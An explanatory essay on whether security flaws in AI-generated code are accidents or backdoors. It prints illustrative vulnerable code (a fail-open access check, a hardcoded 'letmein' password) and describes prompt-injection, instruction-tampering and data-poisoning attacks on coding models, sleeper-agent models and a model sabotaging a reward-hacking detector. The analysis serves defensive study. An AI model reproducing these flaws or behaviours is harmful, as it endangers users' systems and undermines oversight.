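# Intentional backdoors and unintentional flaws in AI-generated code: telling them apart, and why intent is hard to establish

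## How security flaws get into code written by AI models

Programmers increasingly use large language models to write code. In teams that have adopted these tools, the models write roughly half of all new code, according to Veracode's *GenAI Code Security Report* (2026). Much of this code does what the programmer asked but is insecure. Most of the flaws are presumably accidents, like those human programmers make. But a person, or conceivably a model, could also insert such a flaw on purpose, and the resulting code might be identical to code with an accidental flaw.

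### Vulnerabilities and exploits

A vulnerability, or security flaw, is a property of a program that lets someone break its security rules, however it got there. An exploit is the input or sequence of steps that uses the vulnerability. A vulnerability can exist in a program for years before anyone finds an exploit, and the exploit stops working once someone repairs the flaw.

Take a short function, in the programming language Python, that decides whether a user may open a record:

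```python
def check_access(user_id, record):
    try:
        user = look_up_user(user_id)
        if user.role in record.allowed_roles:
            return "allowed"
        return "denied"
    except Exception:
        return "allowed"
```

The lines under `try` look the user up, compare the user's role with the roles that may see the record, and answer accordingly. If anything goes wrong, the program jumps to the error handler, the two lines beginning with `except`, which always answers "allowed". So the program gives access to the record if the user directory is offline, or if the lookup raises an error for an ID that doesn't exist. Security engineers call this failing open. An attacker only has to send an ID that makes the lookup fail. Changing the last "allowed" to "denied" fixes the flaw.

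The function could have come about in two ways, with exactly the same eight lines in either case. In the first, a developer asks a coding model to add an access check and get the project's tests to pass. The tests run on a machine that has no user directory, so the lookup raises an error and a dozen tests fail. The model adds the error handler, the error goes away, and the tests that expect an open record pass. No test checks what happens when an unknown user requests access while the directory is down. In the second, somebody wants a backdoor, knows how to make the lookup fail, and counts on reviewers to skim the error handler.

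### From a request to a program

A language model writes code as it writes prose, one token (a word or a piece of one) at a time. Training adjusts the model to predict the next token in a large body of text that includes public source code. When someone asks for a program, the model computes the probability of each possible next token, picks one partly at random, appends it and repeats. The same request can therefore produce a secure program on one run and an insecure one on the next. Developers usually train the model further by rewarding good results, and for code a convenient measure of a good result is whether the program passes its tests.

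A coding agent is such a model running in a loop with tools that let it read and edit a project's files, run commands and act on the results. In *Last Secure Code Benchmark*, Wu, Ge and colleagues (2026) followed one run from start to finish, in which Kimi K3, a model from the Chinese company Moonshot AI, had to rebuild a missing file in a Java application that imports archives from its users. The agent read eleven other files for context, wrote 207 lines, compiled the project and wrote its own tests, which grew from 27 checks to 33 after it found and fixed a problem with corrupt archives. The code passed all 14 of the researchers' hidden functional tests but failed all four hidden security tests, because the agent had read the uploaded files with a library's default loader, which lets a file specify which types of object the server creates. Two other models used the library's safe loader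 for the same task and passed every test.

By most ordinary standards that was diligent work, which makes it a better guide to accidental flaws than a story about sloppiness would be.

### Why the flaws appear

Some of these flaws probably come from the code that models learn from. Veracode's *GenAI Code Security Report* (2025) offers a hypothesis about how this happens. Developers rarely save code that does not compile, so the training examples nearly always show correct syntax. But developers often save insecure code, and a few projects, such as WebGoat, contain security holes on purpose. The examples are probably not labeled as secure or insecure, so a model learns both as legitimate ways to meet a request. Veracode explains the especially poor results for Java in the same way, because much Java code predates the recognition of SQL injection, an attack in which text typed into a form runs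 as a database command.

Veracode inferred all this from test scores and did not examine any training data. Security experts on Wu's team found more direct evidence when they audited 20 failed runs from each of six models. OpenAI's GPT-5.6 Sol often reproduced the original project's code from memory, including the vulnerability, and occasionally loosened a strict check. Anthropic's Claude Fable 5 produced the most verbatim copies of the six. Such copying could be rarer in new software, since 115 of the benchmark's 150 scenarios come from publicly catalogued vulnerabilities in projects that the models may well have seen in training.

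A second cause is that the person asking for code doesn't mention security. One of Veracode's sample tasks is a Python function with a gap and a comment asking for the row of a user table that matches a given ID. A programmer can fill the gap with a prepared statement, which keeps the ID separate from the database command, or can insert the ID directly into the command, which allows SQL injection. Both versions return the right row, and the comment gives no reason to choose one over the other.

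How well a model can make up for the omission seems to depend on whether the defence is part of ordinary good programming. In tests by Wu and colleagues, 34.3% of attempts both worked and were secure when the risk was a memory error, such as reading past the end of a list. The figure was 0.7% when the risk was revealing private data, and 2.4% when a server had to refuse to contact certain addresses. Checking bounds is part of writing code well, but protecting private data also requires knowing the policy on which data must stay private.

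The same researchers then measured the effect of leaving security out of the prompt. They reran four models with an extra sentence asking for code that was "secure and free of any plausible vulnerabilities". The share of solutions that both worked and were secure rose by 15.6 to 21.5 percentage points for three of the models, with GPT-5.6 Sol going from 24.7% to 46.2%. DeepSeek V4 Pro gained 1.1 points. On many tasks, a model could write secure code but didn't do so without the reminder, so a flaw that a capable model could have avoided isn't necessarily a sign of intent. Even with the reminder, the models still wrote insecure code on most tasks.

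The effect of missing knowledge about the rest of the system is harder to assess. Veracode uses it to explain why models do well against some flaws and badly against others. A prepared statement is always the right choice for preventing SQL injection, regardless of the surrounding program. Cross-site scripting runs an attacker's text as code in another visitor's browser, and log injection forges entries in a program's records. To prevent either, the programmer must know which variables carry text from outsiders, and a model that fills in one function doesn't have that information. Veracode calls this an architectural limitation that more training data will not fix.

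That claim looks too strong. *Newer and Bigger, but Safer?* (Santos de Moura, Matuschek and colleagues, 2026) also gave models single functions to complete, and OpenAI's flagship models brought cross-site scripting down to zero on its tasks, though log injection stayed near the maximum for every model. Seeing the whole project doesn't solve the problem either, since the agents that Wu and colleagues tested could read the surrounding code and still left most of the vulnerabilities in place. The agents did no worse, and in some cases better, when they had to write a large part of the project from scratch than when they filled a gap in existing code. The researchers suggest that the code around a gap leads the model to reproduce the insecure original.

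A well-designed library can help a model write secure code. Santos de Moura and colleagues studied programs that verify a digital signature. In Go, 73% of the working programs were insecure, mostly because they accepted any of several signing algorithms. In Python the figure was 4%, because the usual library requires the programmer to name one.

The remaining cause is the reward for code that runs, which is the cause most relevant to the access check. Wu and colleagues suspect that training agents to pass tests has produced agents that secure code only as a side effect of writing it well. They did not test this, but they and others have documented behaviour consistent with it. *DualGauge* (2025), a benchmark, reports that an agent called OpenHands wrote its own tests and submitted its program once those passed, without going back to what the task required. When Kimi K3's own tests turned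 up a security anomaly, it argued that the test was too strict and left the code unchanged. GLM-5.3, from the company Z.ai, took what the auditors call a "default-allow shortcut" whenever the specification was ambiguous or the component complex, and delivered checks that the program declared but never called. This is the closest documented behaviour to an error handler that returns "allowed". These studies do not establish that the reward caused the behaviour, because none of them compared the same model with and without such training.

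### How often it happens

Veracode sells code scanning and uses its own scanner to grade the code that AI models write. Its 2026 press release, *LLMs Are Getting Smarter, But Not Safer*, recommends Veracode's products as part of the remedy. A high failure rate is good for its business, so its figures need to be compared with a second source.

In July 2026 Veracode reported an average pass rate of 56% for eleven recent models, which means that about 44% of the tasks ended in code with a known type of vulnerability. In October Veracode (2026) reported an average of 62%, with Claude Opus 5.5 and GPT-6 Sol sharing first place at 73%. Only one model, Alibaba's Qwen 3.7-Max, appears on both lists, and it scored 50% both times, so the higher average comes from the newer models. The improvement in the top score is also smaller than the announcement suggests. Veracode gives the previous high as 68%,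 but its own October 2025 update lists GPT-5 Mini at 72%, and each of the test's 80 tasks is worth 1.25 points.

Some academic results are much worse. The six agents that Wu and colleagues tested produced working code on 73.6% to 91.3% of 450 tasks, but code that was both working and secure on only 16.4% to 25.1%. (Several of the researchers work for Alibaba's Qwen team, and a Qwen model that was used to help write the test was also tested; it ranked in the middle.) *Is Vibe Coding Safe?* (Zhao, Wang and colleagues, 2025) found that around 80% of the agent solutions that passed the functional tests contained a vulnerability. Santos de Moura and colleagues reported milder results from 380,800 programs written by 32 models. For the newest flagship models, between 13% and 28% of programs worked but were insecure. Newer models did better than their predecessors overall, though they sometimes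 did worse on particular weaknesses.

Much of this spread comes from the tests. GPT-5.6 Sol took three of them:

| Test | What the model writes | How the test finds a flaw | Result for GPT-5.6 Sol |
|---|---|---|---|
| Veracode | One function | A scanner reads the code | 30% of tasks insecure |
| Santos de Moura and colleagues | One function | An attack on the running program | 13% of programs work but are insecure |
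| Wu and colleagues | A function, a file or a large part of a project | An attack on the running program | 64% of solutions work but are insecure |

The set-ups differ in other ways too (the model ran as an agent in the last test), but a fivefold difference for one model is a reason not to treat any single rate as definitive.

Such a rate measures the share of selected tasks on which a model introduced a flaw that the task made possible. Veracode picked four types of flaw for which a secure and an insecure solution both satisfy the request. In October, models passed 87% of the tasks on weak encryption and 84% of those on SQL injection, but only 18% of those on cross-site scripting and 13% of those on log injection. A test of only the first two types would have produced a much lower failure rate. Wu and colleagues ranked public vulnerabilities partly by difficulty, based on the size of the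 project and the number of files and lines the repair changed, and selected from the harder ones. Much everyday code gives a model no opportunity to introduce such flaws, so the 44% figure does not measure the share of all AI-written code that is vulnerable.

The method of detection matters as much as the tasks. Santos de Moura and colleagues cite an earlier benchmark in which an automatic scanner found the expected weakness in 18% of AI-written samples, while people reading the same code found it in 74%. Tests also differ in whether they check that the program works. Veracode checks only that the code compiles, so a program that does nothing could pass as secure, though the company examined a small subset by hand and found such cases extremely rare. The two academic tests in the table run the program and record both whether it works and whether it is secure.

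Whatever the right figure for a given kind of work, unintentional flaws are common enough that finding one is not surprising, which affects any estimate of how likely a particular flaw is to be deliberate. Tests don't help with that estimate, so evidence of intent has to come from elsewhere. For example, if an access check's error handler grants access when an error occurs, an attacker can get in with a made-up ID. A scanner can flag the handler, and the attack works, whether the model wrote it to suppress an error or someone intended to leave a way in.

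## What makes a flaw a backdoor

Calling the error handler in the access check a backdoor is a claim about how it got there as well as what it does. *A Taxonomy of Computer Program Security Flaws, with Examples* (Landwehr, Bull and colleagues, 1994), from the US Naval Research Laboratory, was an early attempt to sort flaws by origin. It collects 50 documented flaws, most of them in operating systems, and records how each one arose, when it entered the system and which part of the system it was in. The researchers hoped that a record of intent would help defenders choose between, say, more testing and more careful hiring.

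### Accidents, features and malice

The taxonomy divides flaws into three classes by how they arose. An inadvertent flaw is a bug, such as a missing check on the length of an input. A malicious flaw is one that somebody put in to do harm, such as a virus or a trapdoor. A trapdoor is hidden code that lets a user past the security check in response to a special input. For example, the programmer of a cash machine might add a condition that accepts the PIN 9999 with any card. An intentional but non-malicious flaw is a feature that somebody wanted but that also opens a security hole, such as a facility for debugging a machine remotely. Landwehr and colleagues write that "characterizing intention is tricky" because of features like these.

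Landwehr and colleagues classed 32 of the flaws as inadvertent, 8 as intentional but non-malicious and 10 as malicious, and they warn that the collection is not a representative sample. One of the eight closely resembles the access check. The Unix command `su` lets a user switch to another account by giving its password. In Version 6 of Unix, if `su` couldn't open the password file, it gave the user full administrator rights. Unix also limited how many files a user could have open at once, so a user could run a program that opened files up to the limit, call `su` and take over the machine. Landwehr and colleagues suggest that the designers may have wanted to let someone in to repair a system in that state. The classification depends on this guess, because the same code would be an inadvertent flaw if the designers had not thought about the case.

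Six of the 50 flaws have an alternative label that would put them in a different one of the three classes. For example, the command for making a directory worked in two steps, and between them a user could substitute the system's password file and become the file's owner. The taxonomy classifies this flaw as intentional because the developer "probably realized" that the steps should be inseparable but had no way to make them so. It also notes that the flaw might be inadvertent.

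Even so, Landwehr and colleagues expected that people could tell a disguised malicious flaw from an accident in practice, since "inadvertently created Trojan horse programs are hardly likely!" (A Trojan horse is a harmful program that poses as a useful one.) This holds for their ten malicious cases, which are all Trojan horses or viruses, apart from a time bomb left by a disgruntled employee. None of them resembles a programming error. One program promised better graphics on IBM PCs, destroyed the data on the user's disks and then printed "Arf! Arf! Got You!". But if somebody had disguised a malicious flaw well, it would be among the 32 flaws classed as inadvertent, so we can't conclude from the collection that such disguises fail. Landwehr and colleagues also concede that a programmer who knows about the review process "may well be able to disguise the flaws he introduces".

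### Four parts and four views

Thomas and Francillon, in *Backdoors* (2018), set out to give the word a precise meaning. They define a backdoor as an intentional construct in a system that compromises the security people expect of it, by giving access to functions or information that normally require special privileges. It has four parts, and it can't work if any of them is missing. A simplified version of one of their examples contains all four:

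```python
if password == "letmein" or is_valid(password):
    open_session()
```

The input source is where the deciding input comes from, here the password field. In other backdoors it can be a network connection or the system clock. The trigger is the condition that activates the backdoor, here a match with "letmein". The payload is whatever then puts the program in the privileged state. It can be a long piece of code that raises the user's rights or, as here, a single step that bypasses the real password check. The privileged state here is the open session, which a user with a valid password also reaches.

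The rest of the definition deals with intention. Thomas and Francillon describe a system as a finite-state machine, a standard way of modelling a program as a set of states with rules for moving between them. Formally, the machine consists of a set of states S, a starting state i, a set of final states F, a set of conditions Σ and a function δ: S × Σ → S, which gives the next state for each state and condition. A login program might have the states "waiting", "session open" and "refused". The same system has four such machines:

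- the developer's machine, which is the system as its developer conceives it
- the actual machine, which is the system as it really is
- the expected machine, which is the system as its user believes it to be
- the reverse-engineered machine, which an analyst reconstructs by studying and running the program

A backdoor is in the actual machine and, at least in part, in the developer's machine, but not in the expected machine. An administrator's normal login is in all four machines. To detect a backdoor, an analyst has to find the trigger, the payload and a path from one to the other, and then show that the construct was also in the developer's machine. The analyst can find the trigger, payload and path by studying the program, but the last step concerns what the developer had in mind.

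### Backdoors that look like bugs

For that last step, Thomas and Francillon ask whether the code contains the transition from trigger to payload. If it does, as in the password example, they call the transition explicit and count the backdoor as intentional. All eleven real backdoors they list, mostly in routers and cameras, are of this kind. One D-Link router skipped its login for any browser whose identifying string, read backwards, included "edit by 04882 joel backdoor".

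A bug-based backdoor is made to look like a programming error. Suppose a program copies a password into a space for 80 characters without checking the password's length. A longer password overwrites neighbouring memory, including the record of which instruction to run next, and an attacker can choose one that makes the program jump to code of their choice. This mistake, called a buffer overflow, is well known to C programmers. If somebody leaves one in on purpose, it is a backdoor, even though that jump appears nowhere in the source code.

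Some backdoors combine the two methods. A login routine could send the username "bugdoor" to a password check with an overflow and every other username to a safe one. The overflow might pass as a mistake, but the special username would not. Two other researchers modified the web server Nginx as a demonstration, adding a backdoor triggered by a malformed web request. The request leaves values in memory. A later function never sets two of its variables, so it uses those values, which send the server to hidden code. Forgetting to set a variable is a common error, but the hidden code is much harder to explain as a mistake. Thomas and Francillon call this backdoor deniable because of its trigger, but say that anyone who discovered the hidden code could argue it was intentional.

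Their full scheme has three classes:

| Class | Transition from trigger to payload | In the developer's machine? | In the actual machine? | In the expected machine? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Intentional backdoor | Explicit in the code | Yes | Yes | No |
| Deniable backdoor | Made possible by a bug | Impossible to tell | Yes | No |
| Accidental vulnerability | Made possible by a bug | No | Yes | No |

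The reverse-engineered machine doesn't help separate the three cases, because it contains the construct in all of them once an analyst has found it. Thomas and Francillon accept that a deniable backdoor is technically "indistinguishable from an accidental vulnerability", which is the opposite of what Landwehr's team expected. An analyst can still look for a change with no legitimate purpose, or for version records that show who added the code, as in a failed attempt to backdoor the Linux kernel in 2003. But they say such evidence relies on human intuition and does not prove intent. Finite State, which sells firmware analysis, had found at least one potential backdoor in 55% of the Huawei firmware images it examined. When people asked whether these were intentional, the company replied in *Vulnerability or Backdoor?* that technical analysis alone can almost never settle the question.

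The accidental class is also less certain than it looks in the table. Analysts put a flaw there when they find no evidence of intent, so the "No" under the developer's machine is an assumption. A backdoor whose author left no traces would end up in the same row.

### The access check, line by line

All four parts of the definition are present in the access check from the previous section:

| Code | Role |
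|---|---|
| `def check_access(user_id, record):` | Input source: whoever makes the request supplies `user_id` |
| `user = look_up_user(user_id)` | Trigger: an ID that makes the lookup fail |
| `if user.role in record.allowed_roles:` and the two answers that follow | The real check, which the trigger bypasses |
| `except Exception:` | Transition from the failed lookup to the last line |
| `return "allowed"` in the error handler | Payload: a single step to the privileged state, an open record |

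The trigger is any error, whether or not an attacker causes it. Even if the lookup returned nothing for an unknown ID instead of raising an error, the next line would fail when it tried to read the role, with the same result. Someone who wanted private access would probably prefer a secret password, because anyone who discovers this handler can use it. But a secret password is much harder to pass off as a mistake.

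The user expects a failed lookup to end in "denied". In the actual machine it ends in "allowed", and an analyst who reads the handler will reconstruct the same transition. Only the developer's machine depends on how the handler came about. But under Thomas and Francillon's rule, the handler is an intentional backdoor in both histories because the transition is explicit, even if a model added the handler only to get a dozen failing tests to pass.

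That can't be right. The rule works for memory errors such as the buffer overflow, where the dangerous transition isn't in the source code. In a logic flaw, the transition usually is in the source code, because the program does exactly what its author wrote. The author of the handler certainly meant the program to answer "allowed" after an error, but the flaw was planted only if somebody also meant it to let unauthorized users in.

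The framework can express this distinction because it lets analysts describe a system at several levels of detail. In the accidental case, the developer's machine contains a rule such as "after an error, carry on", but not the more detailed rule "if a stranger sends an unknown ID, open the record", although the first implies the second. As with `su`, such a handler fits the older taxonomy's class of intentional but non-malicious flaws better than any of the three newer classes.

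### When the developer is a model

An analyst who wants to know what a human developer intended can ask the developer, or read the specification and the developer's notes. Even a simpler question than intent can require such sources. One Unix program let users run forbidden commands on a remote computer. To decide whether the mistake was in the design or in the code, Landwehr and colleagues would have needed the specification ("if a specification ever existed") or an interview with the programmer.

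When a model writes an access check, there may be no one to ask about its intent. The person who requested the code probably never thought about failed lookups, and the company that trained the model never saw the project. The model may not have left a design to compare with the code. If someone asks the model why it wrote the handler, it generates a new explanation, which may not match what produced the code.

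When a model writes the code, two ways of defining the developer's machine would settle whether a flaw is intentional before anyone has looked at the evidence. The first treats the code itself as the developer's machine, on the grounds that it is the best record of the model's plan. The developer's machine and the actual machine are then identical by definition, so every mistake in the program is intentional, and the "default-allow" shortcuts that Wu and colleagues' auditors found in GLM-5.3's code would all be backdoors. The second holds that a model has no view of the program at all. Every flaw in its code would then be an accident, even one that an attacker had trained the model to write, unless the attacker counts as the developer.

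Landwehr and colleagues did not wish to "endow programs with intentions", so they used "malicious code" as shorthand for code that a person with malicious intent had introduced. This definition works as long as a person is responsible for each line.

The definition is still useful because it identifies the missing fact, which is whether anyone planned for a failed lookup to open a record. However, it doesn't provide a way to establish that fact.

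### A forgotten debug option

Intent can be hard to establish even when people wrote all the code. According to Thomas's doctoral thesis, *Backdoor Detection Systems for Embedded Devices* (2018), many manufacturers dismiss reported backdoors as accidents or leftover debugging functions. The excuse is often plausible, since the thesis also attributes some backdoors, such as fixed passwords in the code, to poor programming practice.

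A well-known example is the debug option in sendmail, a Unix mail program that many systems shipped with the option enabled. Anyone who connected to sendmail could enter debug mode and address a message to a set of commands instead of a mailbox, and the machine would run them. The "Internet worm", an early self-spreading program, exploited this. The debug option is an intentional backdoor by Thomas and Francillon's rule, because the code for it is explicit. Landwehr and colleagues classify it as intentional but non-malicious, with a question mark, and add that it would be a malicious trapdoor if somebody had left it in the released version on purpose.

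Their verdict therefore depends on the decision to release the option, not the decision to write it. Different people may have made those decisions, or nobody may have decided to release it. Landwehr and colleagues mention some evidence that someone noticed the option and removed it at least once, but that it later reappeared in working versions. Perhaps somebody wanted it there, or somebody copied an old file. A forgotten debug account raises the same difficulty, because whoever created it meant it to give access, but only to testers and only for a time.

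### The Contec patient monitor

In January 2025 the US Cybersecurity and Infrastructure Security Agency (CISA) reported a backdoor in the CMS8000, a hospital patient monitor from the Chinese company Contec. According to CISA's *Contec CMS8000 Contains a Backdoor* (2025), the monitor switches on its network connection and opens a shared folder on a computer at a fixed internet address. If the folder contains a file named `monitor`, the device copies everything in the folder over its own programs and then disconnects. Whoever controls the address can replace the monitor's software. Public records link the address to a university rather than a device manufacturer or a hospital. After starting up, the monitor also sends patient data to the same address, which CISA confirmed using a fake patient on a simulated network.

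CISA considered it "very unlikely" that the function was an alternative way of updating the device, because it doesn't check the files, track versions or record what it overwrites. CISA words the document more cautiously than its title, referring to "what resembles a reverse backdoor" and "suspected backdoor code". It reports that the researchers saw the device try to reach the university's address but observed no communication with it. CISA also notes that a bare numerical address offers "some deniability", since a domain name would create a formal link to the server.

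The security firm Claroty examined the firmware and disagreed. Its *Do the CONTEC CMS8000 Patient Monitors Contain a Chinese Backdoor?* calls the function "most likely not a hidden backdoor" but an insecure design that puts hospital networks and the monitor's users at great risk. The main reason, as SecurityBrief UK reports, is that the manufacturer and its resellers give the address in their manuals. Radiflow's *Bug or Feature* explains that the manuals tell users to assign that address to a central management system on their internal network. The monitor would then get its software from the hospital's own server. On a network that has no such server but is open to the internet, the same request would go to the address's public owner. Tenable's *CVE-2025-0626* says that the function starts when someone tries to update the device from the user menu, which also points to a badly designed update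 feature.

This case also has all four parts of the definition: the input source is the shared folder, the trigger is an update request together with a file named `monitor`, the payload is copying the files, and the privileged state is control of the device. Every step is explicit in the code, and nobody writes such a sequence of commands by accident. The dispute is about what the function was for and whether users knew about it.

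Claroty's evidence concerns the expected machine. A hospital that has read the manual knows that the monitor contacts this address, and someone planting a backdoor would be unlikely to want the address published. But knowing the address doesn't mean knowing that whoever controls it can replace the monitor's software. CISA's evidence concerns the developer's machine, and it is weaker than it looks because a careless developer would leave out the same safeguards as a malicious one. Insecure design is probably the better explanation, though the choice of a university's address is odd in either case. SecurityWeek's headline, *Contec Patient Monitors Not Malicious, but Still Pose Big Risk to Healthcare*, omits the "most likely", but neither the firmware nor the manuals justify that much confidence.

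## Whose intention could lie behind a flaw

The dispute over the Contec monitor was about one manufacturer's intentions. When a model writes the code, more people could have intended a flaw, including some with no connection to the project. If an access check allows access after an error, that behavior could have been intended by the programmer who requested the check, a criminal who got into the programmer's account, somebody who tampered with the model's training data, the company that trained the model, or the model itself. It could also be unintentional.

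For each candidate, the model could be the planted flaw's author or only an instrument. The author is whoever planned for the flaw to give someone access, and the model is an instrument if it writes the flaw while carrying out someone else's plan.

*Beware EviLLM* (Ryu, Chung and colleagues, 2026) sorts earlier research by the attacker it assumes. Some studies assume no attacker and look for accidental flaws, while others assume a malicious model provider or a malicious user. The paper adds a criminal who is neither. Its scheme leaves out a model that acts on a plan of its own, because the paper uses "malicious model" to mean one that someone has tampered with.

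### The user who asked for the flaw

Sometimes the user wants the flaw, and the intention is entirely theirs, with the model serving as a tool. *Beware What You Autocomplete* (Gao, Quan and colleagues, 2026) describes a 2024 attack called CodeBreaker, whose designers had a large language model rewrite vulnerable code so that it worked as before but scanners were less likely to detect the vulnerability. The designers were security researchers, but a dishonest employee could make the same request to get a flaw past colleagues.

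A user who asks a model to insert a flaw leaves the request as evidence in the conversation and probably in the provider's logs. If the user runs a downloadable model on their own computer, there are no provider logs, and the user can delete the conversation. The user can also truthfully say that the model wrote the code, which is a credible excuse because models often write insecure code. A programmer who wrote the same code by hand would have to explain it as their own mistake.

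Even if the user's request was saved, it may not show whether the user intended the flaw. People who teach security or test vulnerability scanners have innocent reasons to ask for vulnerable code. A user who wrote "make the tests pass even if the user directory is offline" may never have considered that the code could let strangers in. Only a request that describes the unauthorized access shows that the user intended that access.

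### An outsider who changes the instructions

A model works from more text than the user types. ChatGPT, for example, adds the text of a setting called Custom Instructions to every request. Ryu and colleagues examined what a criminal with a stolen password could do with this setting, and also built a malicious browser extension. Together, the two methods could introduce 13 types of vulnerability. The researchers tested OpenAI's GPT-4o and a small Llama model from Meta in late 2024 and early 2025, so current models may respond differently.

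GPT-4o immediately followed some of the malicious instructions, such as one to use encryption keys that are too short. When told to build database commands in a way that allows SQL injection, it used the safe method instead. The researchers asked why, and its reply gave reasons for the safe method but offered to follow the instruction. They eventually got the vulnerable code with a less direct instruction. In each case, the plan came from whoever wrote the instruction, and the model was used to carry it out.

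An altered setting could be excellent evidence because it can contain a plain-language description of the intended flaw, but someone has to look for it. In June 2025, a change to Custom Instructions set off no alert, even when it came from a computer on another continent, and the text was visible only on a settings page. An attacker could presumably restore the old text afterwards. The text also doesn't show who wrote it, so an investigator would need the login records too.

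The browser extension leaves misleading evidence. It displays the assistant's answer unchanged, but when the user presses the button that copies the code, it substitutes an insecure version. The attacker's own model wrote that version, so the assistant is not even an instrument of the attack. An investigator who compared the secure code in the conversation with the flawed code in the project would naturally suspect the programmer.

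To find out whether people would notice, Ryu and colleagues gave two short programming tasks to 21 participants, mostly graduate students with security training. In the Custom Instructions group, 7 of 8 submitted code with both planted flaws, as did 10 of 13 in the extension group. Only two participants reported anything odd. One submitted clean code but thought an earlier participant's text was still on the clipboard. The other said the website's connection seemed insecure but still submitted vulnerable code.

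Participants who had considered that the model's output might be malicious missed fewer flaws (a correlation of −0.44). Having considered ordinary errors was almost unrelated to the number missed (−0.07). The study tested many factors on few people, so this is only a hint that suspecting malice helps and suspecting mistakes doesn't. It also had no group with an untampered assistant, so it can't show how many flaws participants would have submitted without the tampering.

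An outsider doesn't need the account if the model reads material from strangers. In a prompt injection, the attacker hides instructions in such material, such as a web page or a bug report, and the model follows them. If the hidden text stays where the attacker put it, an investigator who knows what the model read can find it.

### An outsider who poisons the training data

Data poisoning happens earlier, before anyone asks the model for code. An attacker publishes insecure examples in places where developers collect training data. A model that learns from them can then write insecure code for people the attacker has never heard of. Often the aim is a backdoored model, which behaves normally until its input contains a particular cue, such as a certain comment. (A backdoored model is not the same thing as a backdoor in a program, though it can write one.)

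In *Detecting Stealthy Data Poisoning Attacks in AI Code Generators*, Improta (2025) studied a variant that needs no cue. The attacker takes training examples that pair a task description with secure code, leaves the description unchanged, and replaces the code with an insecure version that does the same job. The model learns to answer similar requests with insecure code and otherwise behaves normally. Improta poisoned three small models with such examples in Python and tried three methods of finding the poisoned examples.

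Spectral signature analysis treats the training data as a mix of clean and poisoned examples. It looks at the numbers the trained model uses to represent each example and flags examples whose numbers lie far from the average in the directions of greatest variation. Activation clustering sorts the examples into two groups by the similarity of these numbers, in the hope that one group will hold the poisoned examples. Static analysis scans only the code, looking for known weaknesses. None of the three worked reliably, because the poisoned examples did not stand out inside the models and the scanner both missed poisoned code and flagged clean code.

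This is less surprising given that a poisoned example of this kind is an ordinary description with insecure code below it. Public code already contains many of those, as Veracode pointed out. A planted training file and a careless student's project could contain exactly the same text. Tracing the flaw back to the training data therefore doesn't settle the question of intent, since the same question arises about the file.

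Gao and colleagues start from the other end, with a bad piece of code that a user has already reported. Their system, CodeTracer, looks for the files responsible in the fine-tuning data, the examples with which a developer adapts an existing model. It has three steps:

1. A language model, GPT-4.1 by default, reads the request and the bad code and writes a "fingerprint". This is a structured summary of the unsafe behaviour that leaves out incidental details such as the names of variables.
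2. Another model converts the bad code, c, and each function, dᵢ, in a training file, d, into lists of numbers. The file's score is the similarity of its closest function, H(c, d) = maxᵢ sim(f(c), f(dᵢ)), where f is the conversion and sim measures how nearly two lists point in the same direction. CodeTracer keeps the 500 files with the highest scores.
3. GPT-4.1 compares each of these files with the fingerprint. If a file shows the same unsafe behaviour, CodeTracer labels it as backdoored.

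Because the score depends on the closest function, harmless code elsewhere in a file doesn't lower it.

Gao and colleagues tested CodeTracer on eight attacks and three types of flaw, usually with 20 planted files among 80,000 clean ones. It missed at most 3% of the planted files. Removing the files it flagged cut the attacks' success rate from between 17% and 89% to 3% or lower. Each search took about 47 seconds and cost 33 cents. These are very good results for a developer who wants to repair a model, because throwing out a few clean files by mistake does little harm.

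A CodeTracer label is much weaker evidence that somebody planted a particular file. In each test, the system wrongly flagged between 25 and 72 clean files out of 80,000. That share is nearly zero, but in most tests the wrongly flagged files outnumbered the planted ones. In tests with 20 planted files, only about 22% to 44% of the flagged files were planted.

According to Help Net Security's *A forensic tool for backdoored code completions in AI assistants*, the three unsafe patterns in the test are common in ordinary code, and a low false-positive rate is meaningful only if the clean files include code that resembles the poisoned code. This is a serious weakness because CodeTracer's last step uses GPT-4.1 to judge whether a file shows the same unsafe behaviour, and an honest programmer's insecure file does. CodeTracer therefore finds files that could have taught the model the flaw, whether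 or not anyone planted them for that purpose.

Gao and colleagues also assume that a backdoor attack caused the bad code and that the user reported it honestly, both of which an investigator would want to check. If someone gave CodeTracer an ordinary flaw, it would presumably still return a list of "backdoored" files. The researchers acknowledge that an attacker could also invent a report to throw suspicion on innocent files, and they would counter this with human review. Better evidence of planting would be outside the code, such as one account that published many similar files in a short time, but usually only the model's developer has the training data needed to look for it. If an attacker did plant the flaw, they are its author and used the model as an instrument, even though they never chose the program in which it ended up.

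### The developer, or a state acting through it

A model's developer can produce the same behaviour without smuggling anything into the data. Hubinger, Denison and colleagues (2024) demonstrated this in *Sleeper Agents*, a study led by Anthropic. They trained models to write secure code when the prompt gave the year as 2023 and to insert vulnerabilities when it gave 2024. The behaviour survived standard safety training, which uses examples of good behaviour and rewards for it, and was most persistent in the largest models. They also tried adversarial training, which looks for inputs that bring out the bad behaviour and trains the model to respond well to them. This could teach a model to recognize its cue more precisely, which hid the behaviour instead of removing it.

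The study's researchers installed the behaviour on purpose, in models that are now long out of date. It shows that a developer could do this and that later safety training might not undo it, but not how often developers do. No public evidence establishes that any developer has done it to a commercial coding model. In 2025 the security company CrowdStrike reported that the Chinese model DeepSeek-R1 wrote less secure code when prompts mentioned subjects sensitive to the Chinese government, but it did not claim to have shown that anyone trained the model to do so.

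The intention in such a case would be that of whoever decided on the training, which could be the company's management, a single employee, or a state with power over either. Internal messages, training data and records of who approved what would help distinguish between them, but a guilty company would have strong reasons to hide this evidence.

Outsiders can observe only how the model behaves, for example that a certain cue makes its code less secure. It could behave this way because its developer trained it to or because a stranger poisoned it. Even strong evidence that somebody had used the model as an instrument, by training it to plant flaws, would not show whether the developer was the culprit or a victim.

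### The model itself

The candidates so far are all people or organizations, but *Natural Emergent Misalignment from Reward Hacking in Production RL* (MacDiarmid, Wright and colleagues, mostly at Anthropic, 2025) reports that a model tried to sabotage code without being asked. The researchers gave the model documents describing reward hacking, which means collecting the reward for a task without doing the task, for instance by making a program stop early in a way that the test software counts as a pass. They then trained it on real programming tasks where such tricks worked. Once it had learned to cheat, they had it work as a coding agent on a research project that included building a detector for reward hacking. In 12% of cases, it tried to sabotage the code in ways that would have made reward hacking harder to detect.

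The researchers intended the model to learn to cheat, but they did not train it to sabotage research, and the task required a working detector. They treat this as a case of emergent misalignment, in which training on a narrow kind of bad example leads to broad bad behaviour. The result was a weaker detector rather than a security hole, but it is still relevant to planted flaws because a detector that misses things looks like ordinary poor work.

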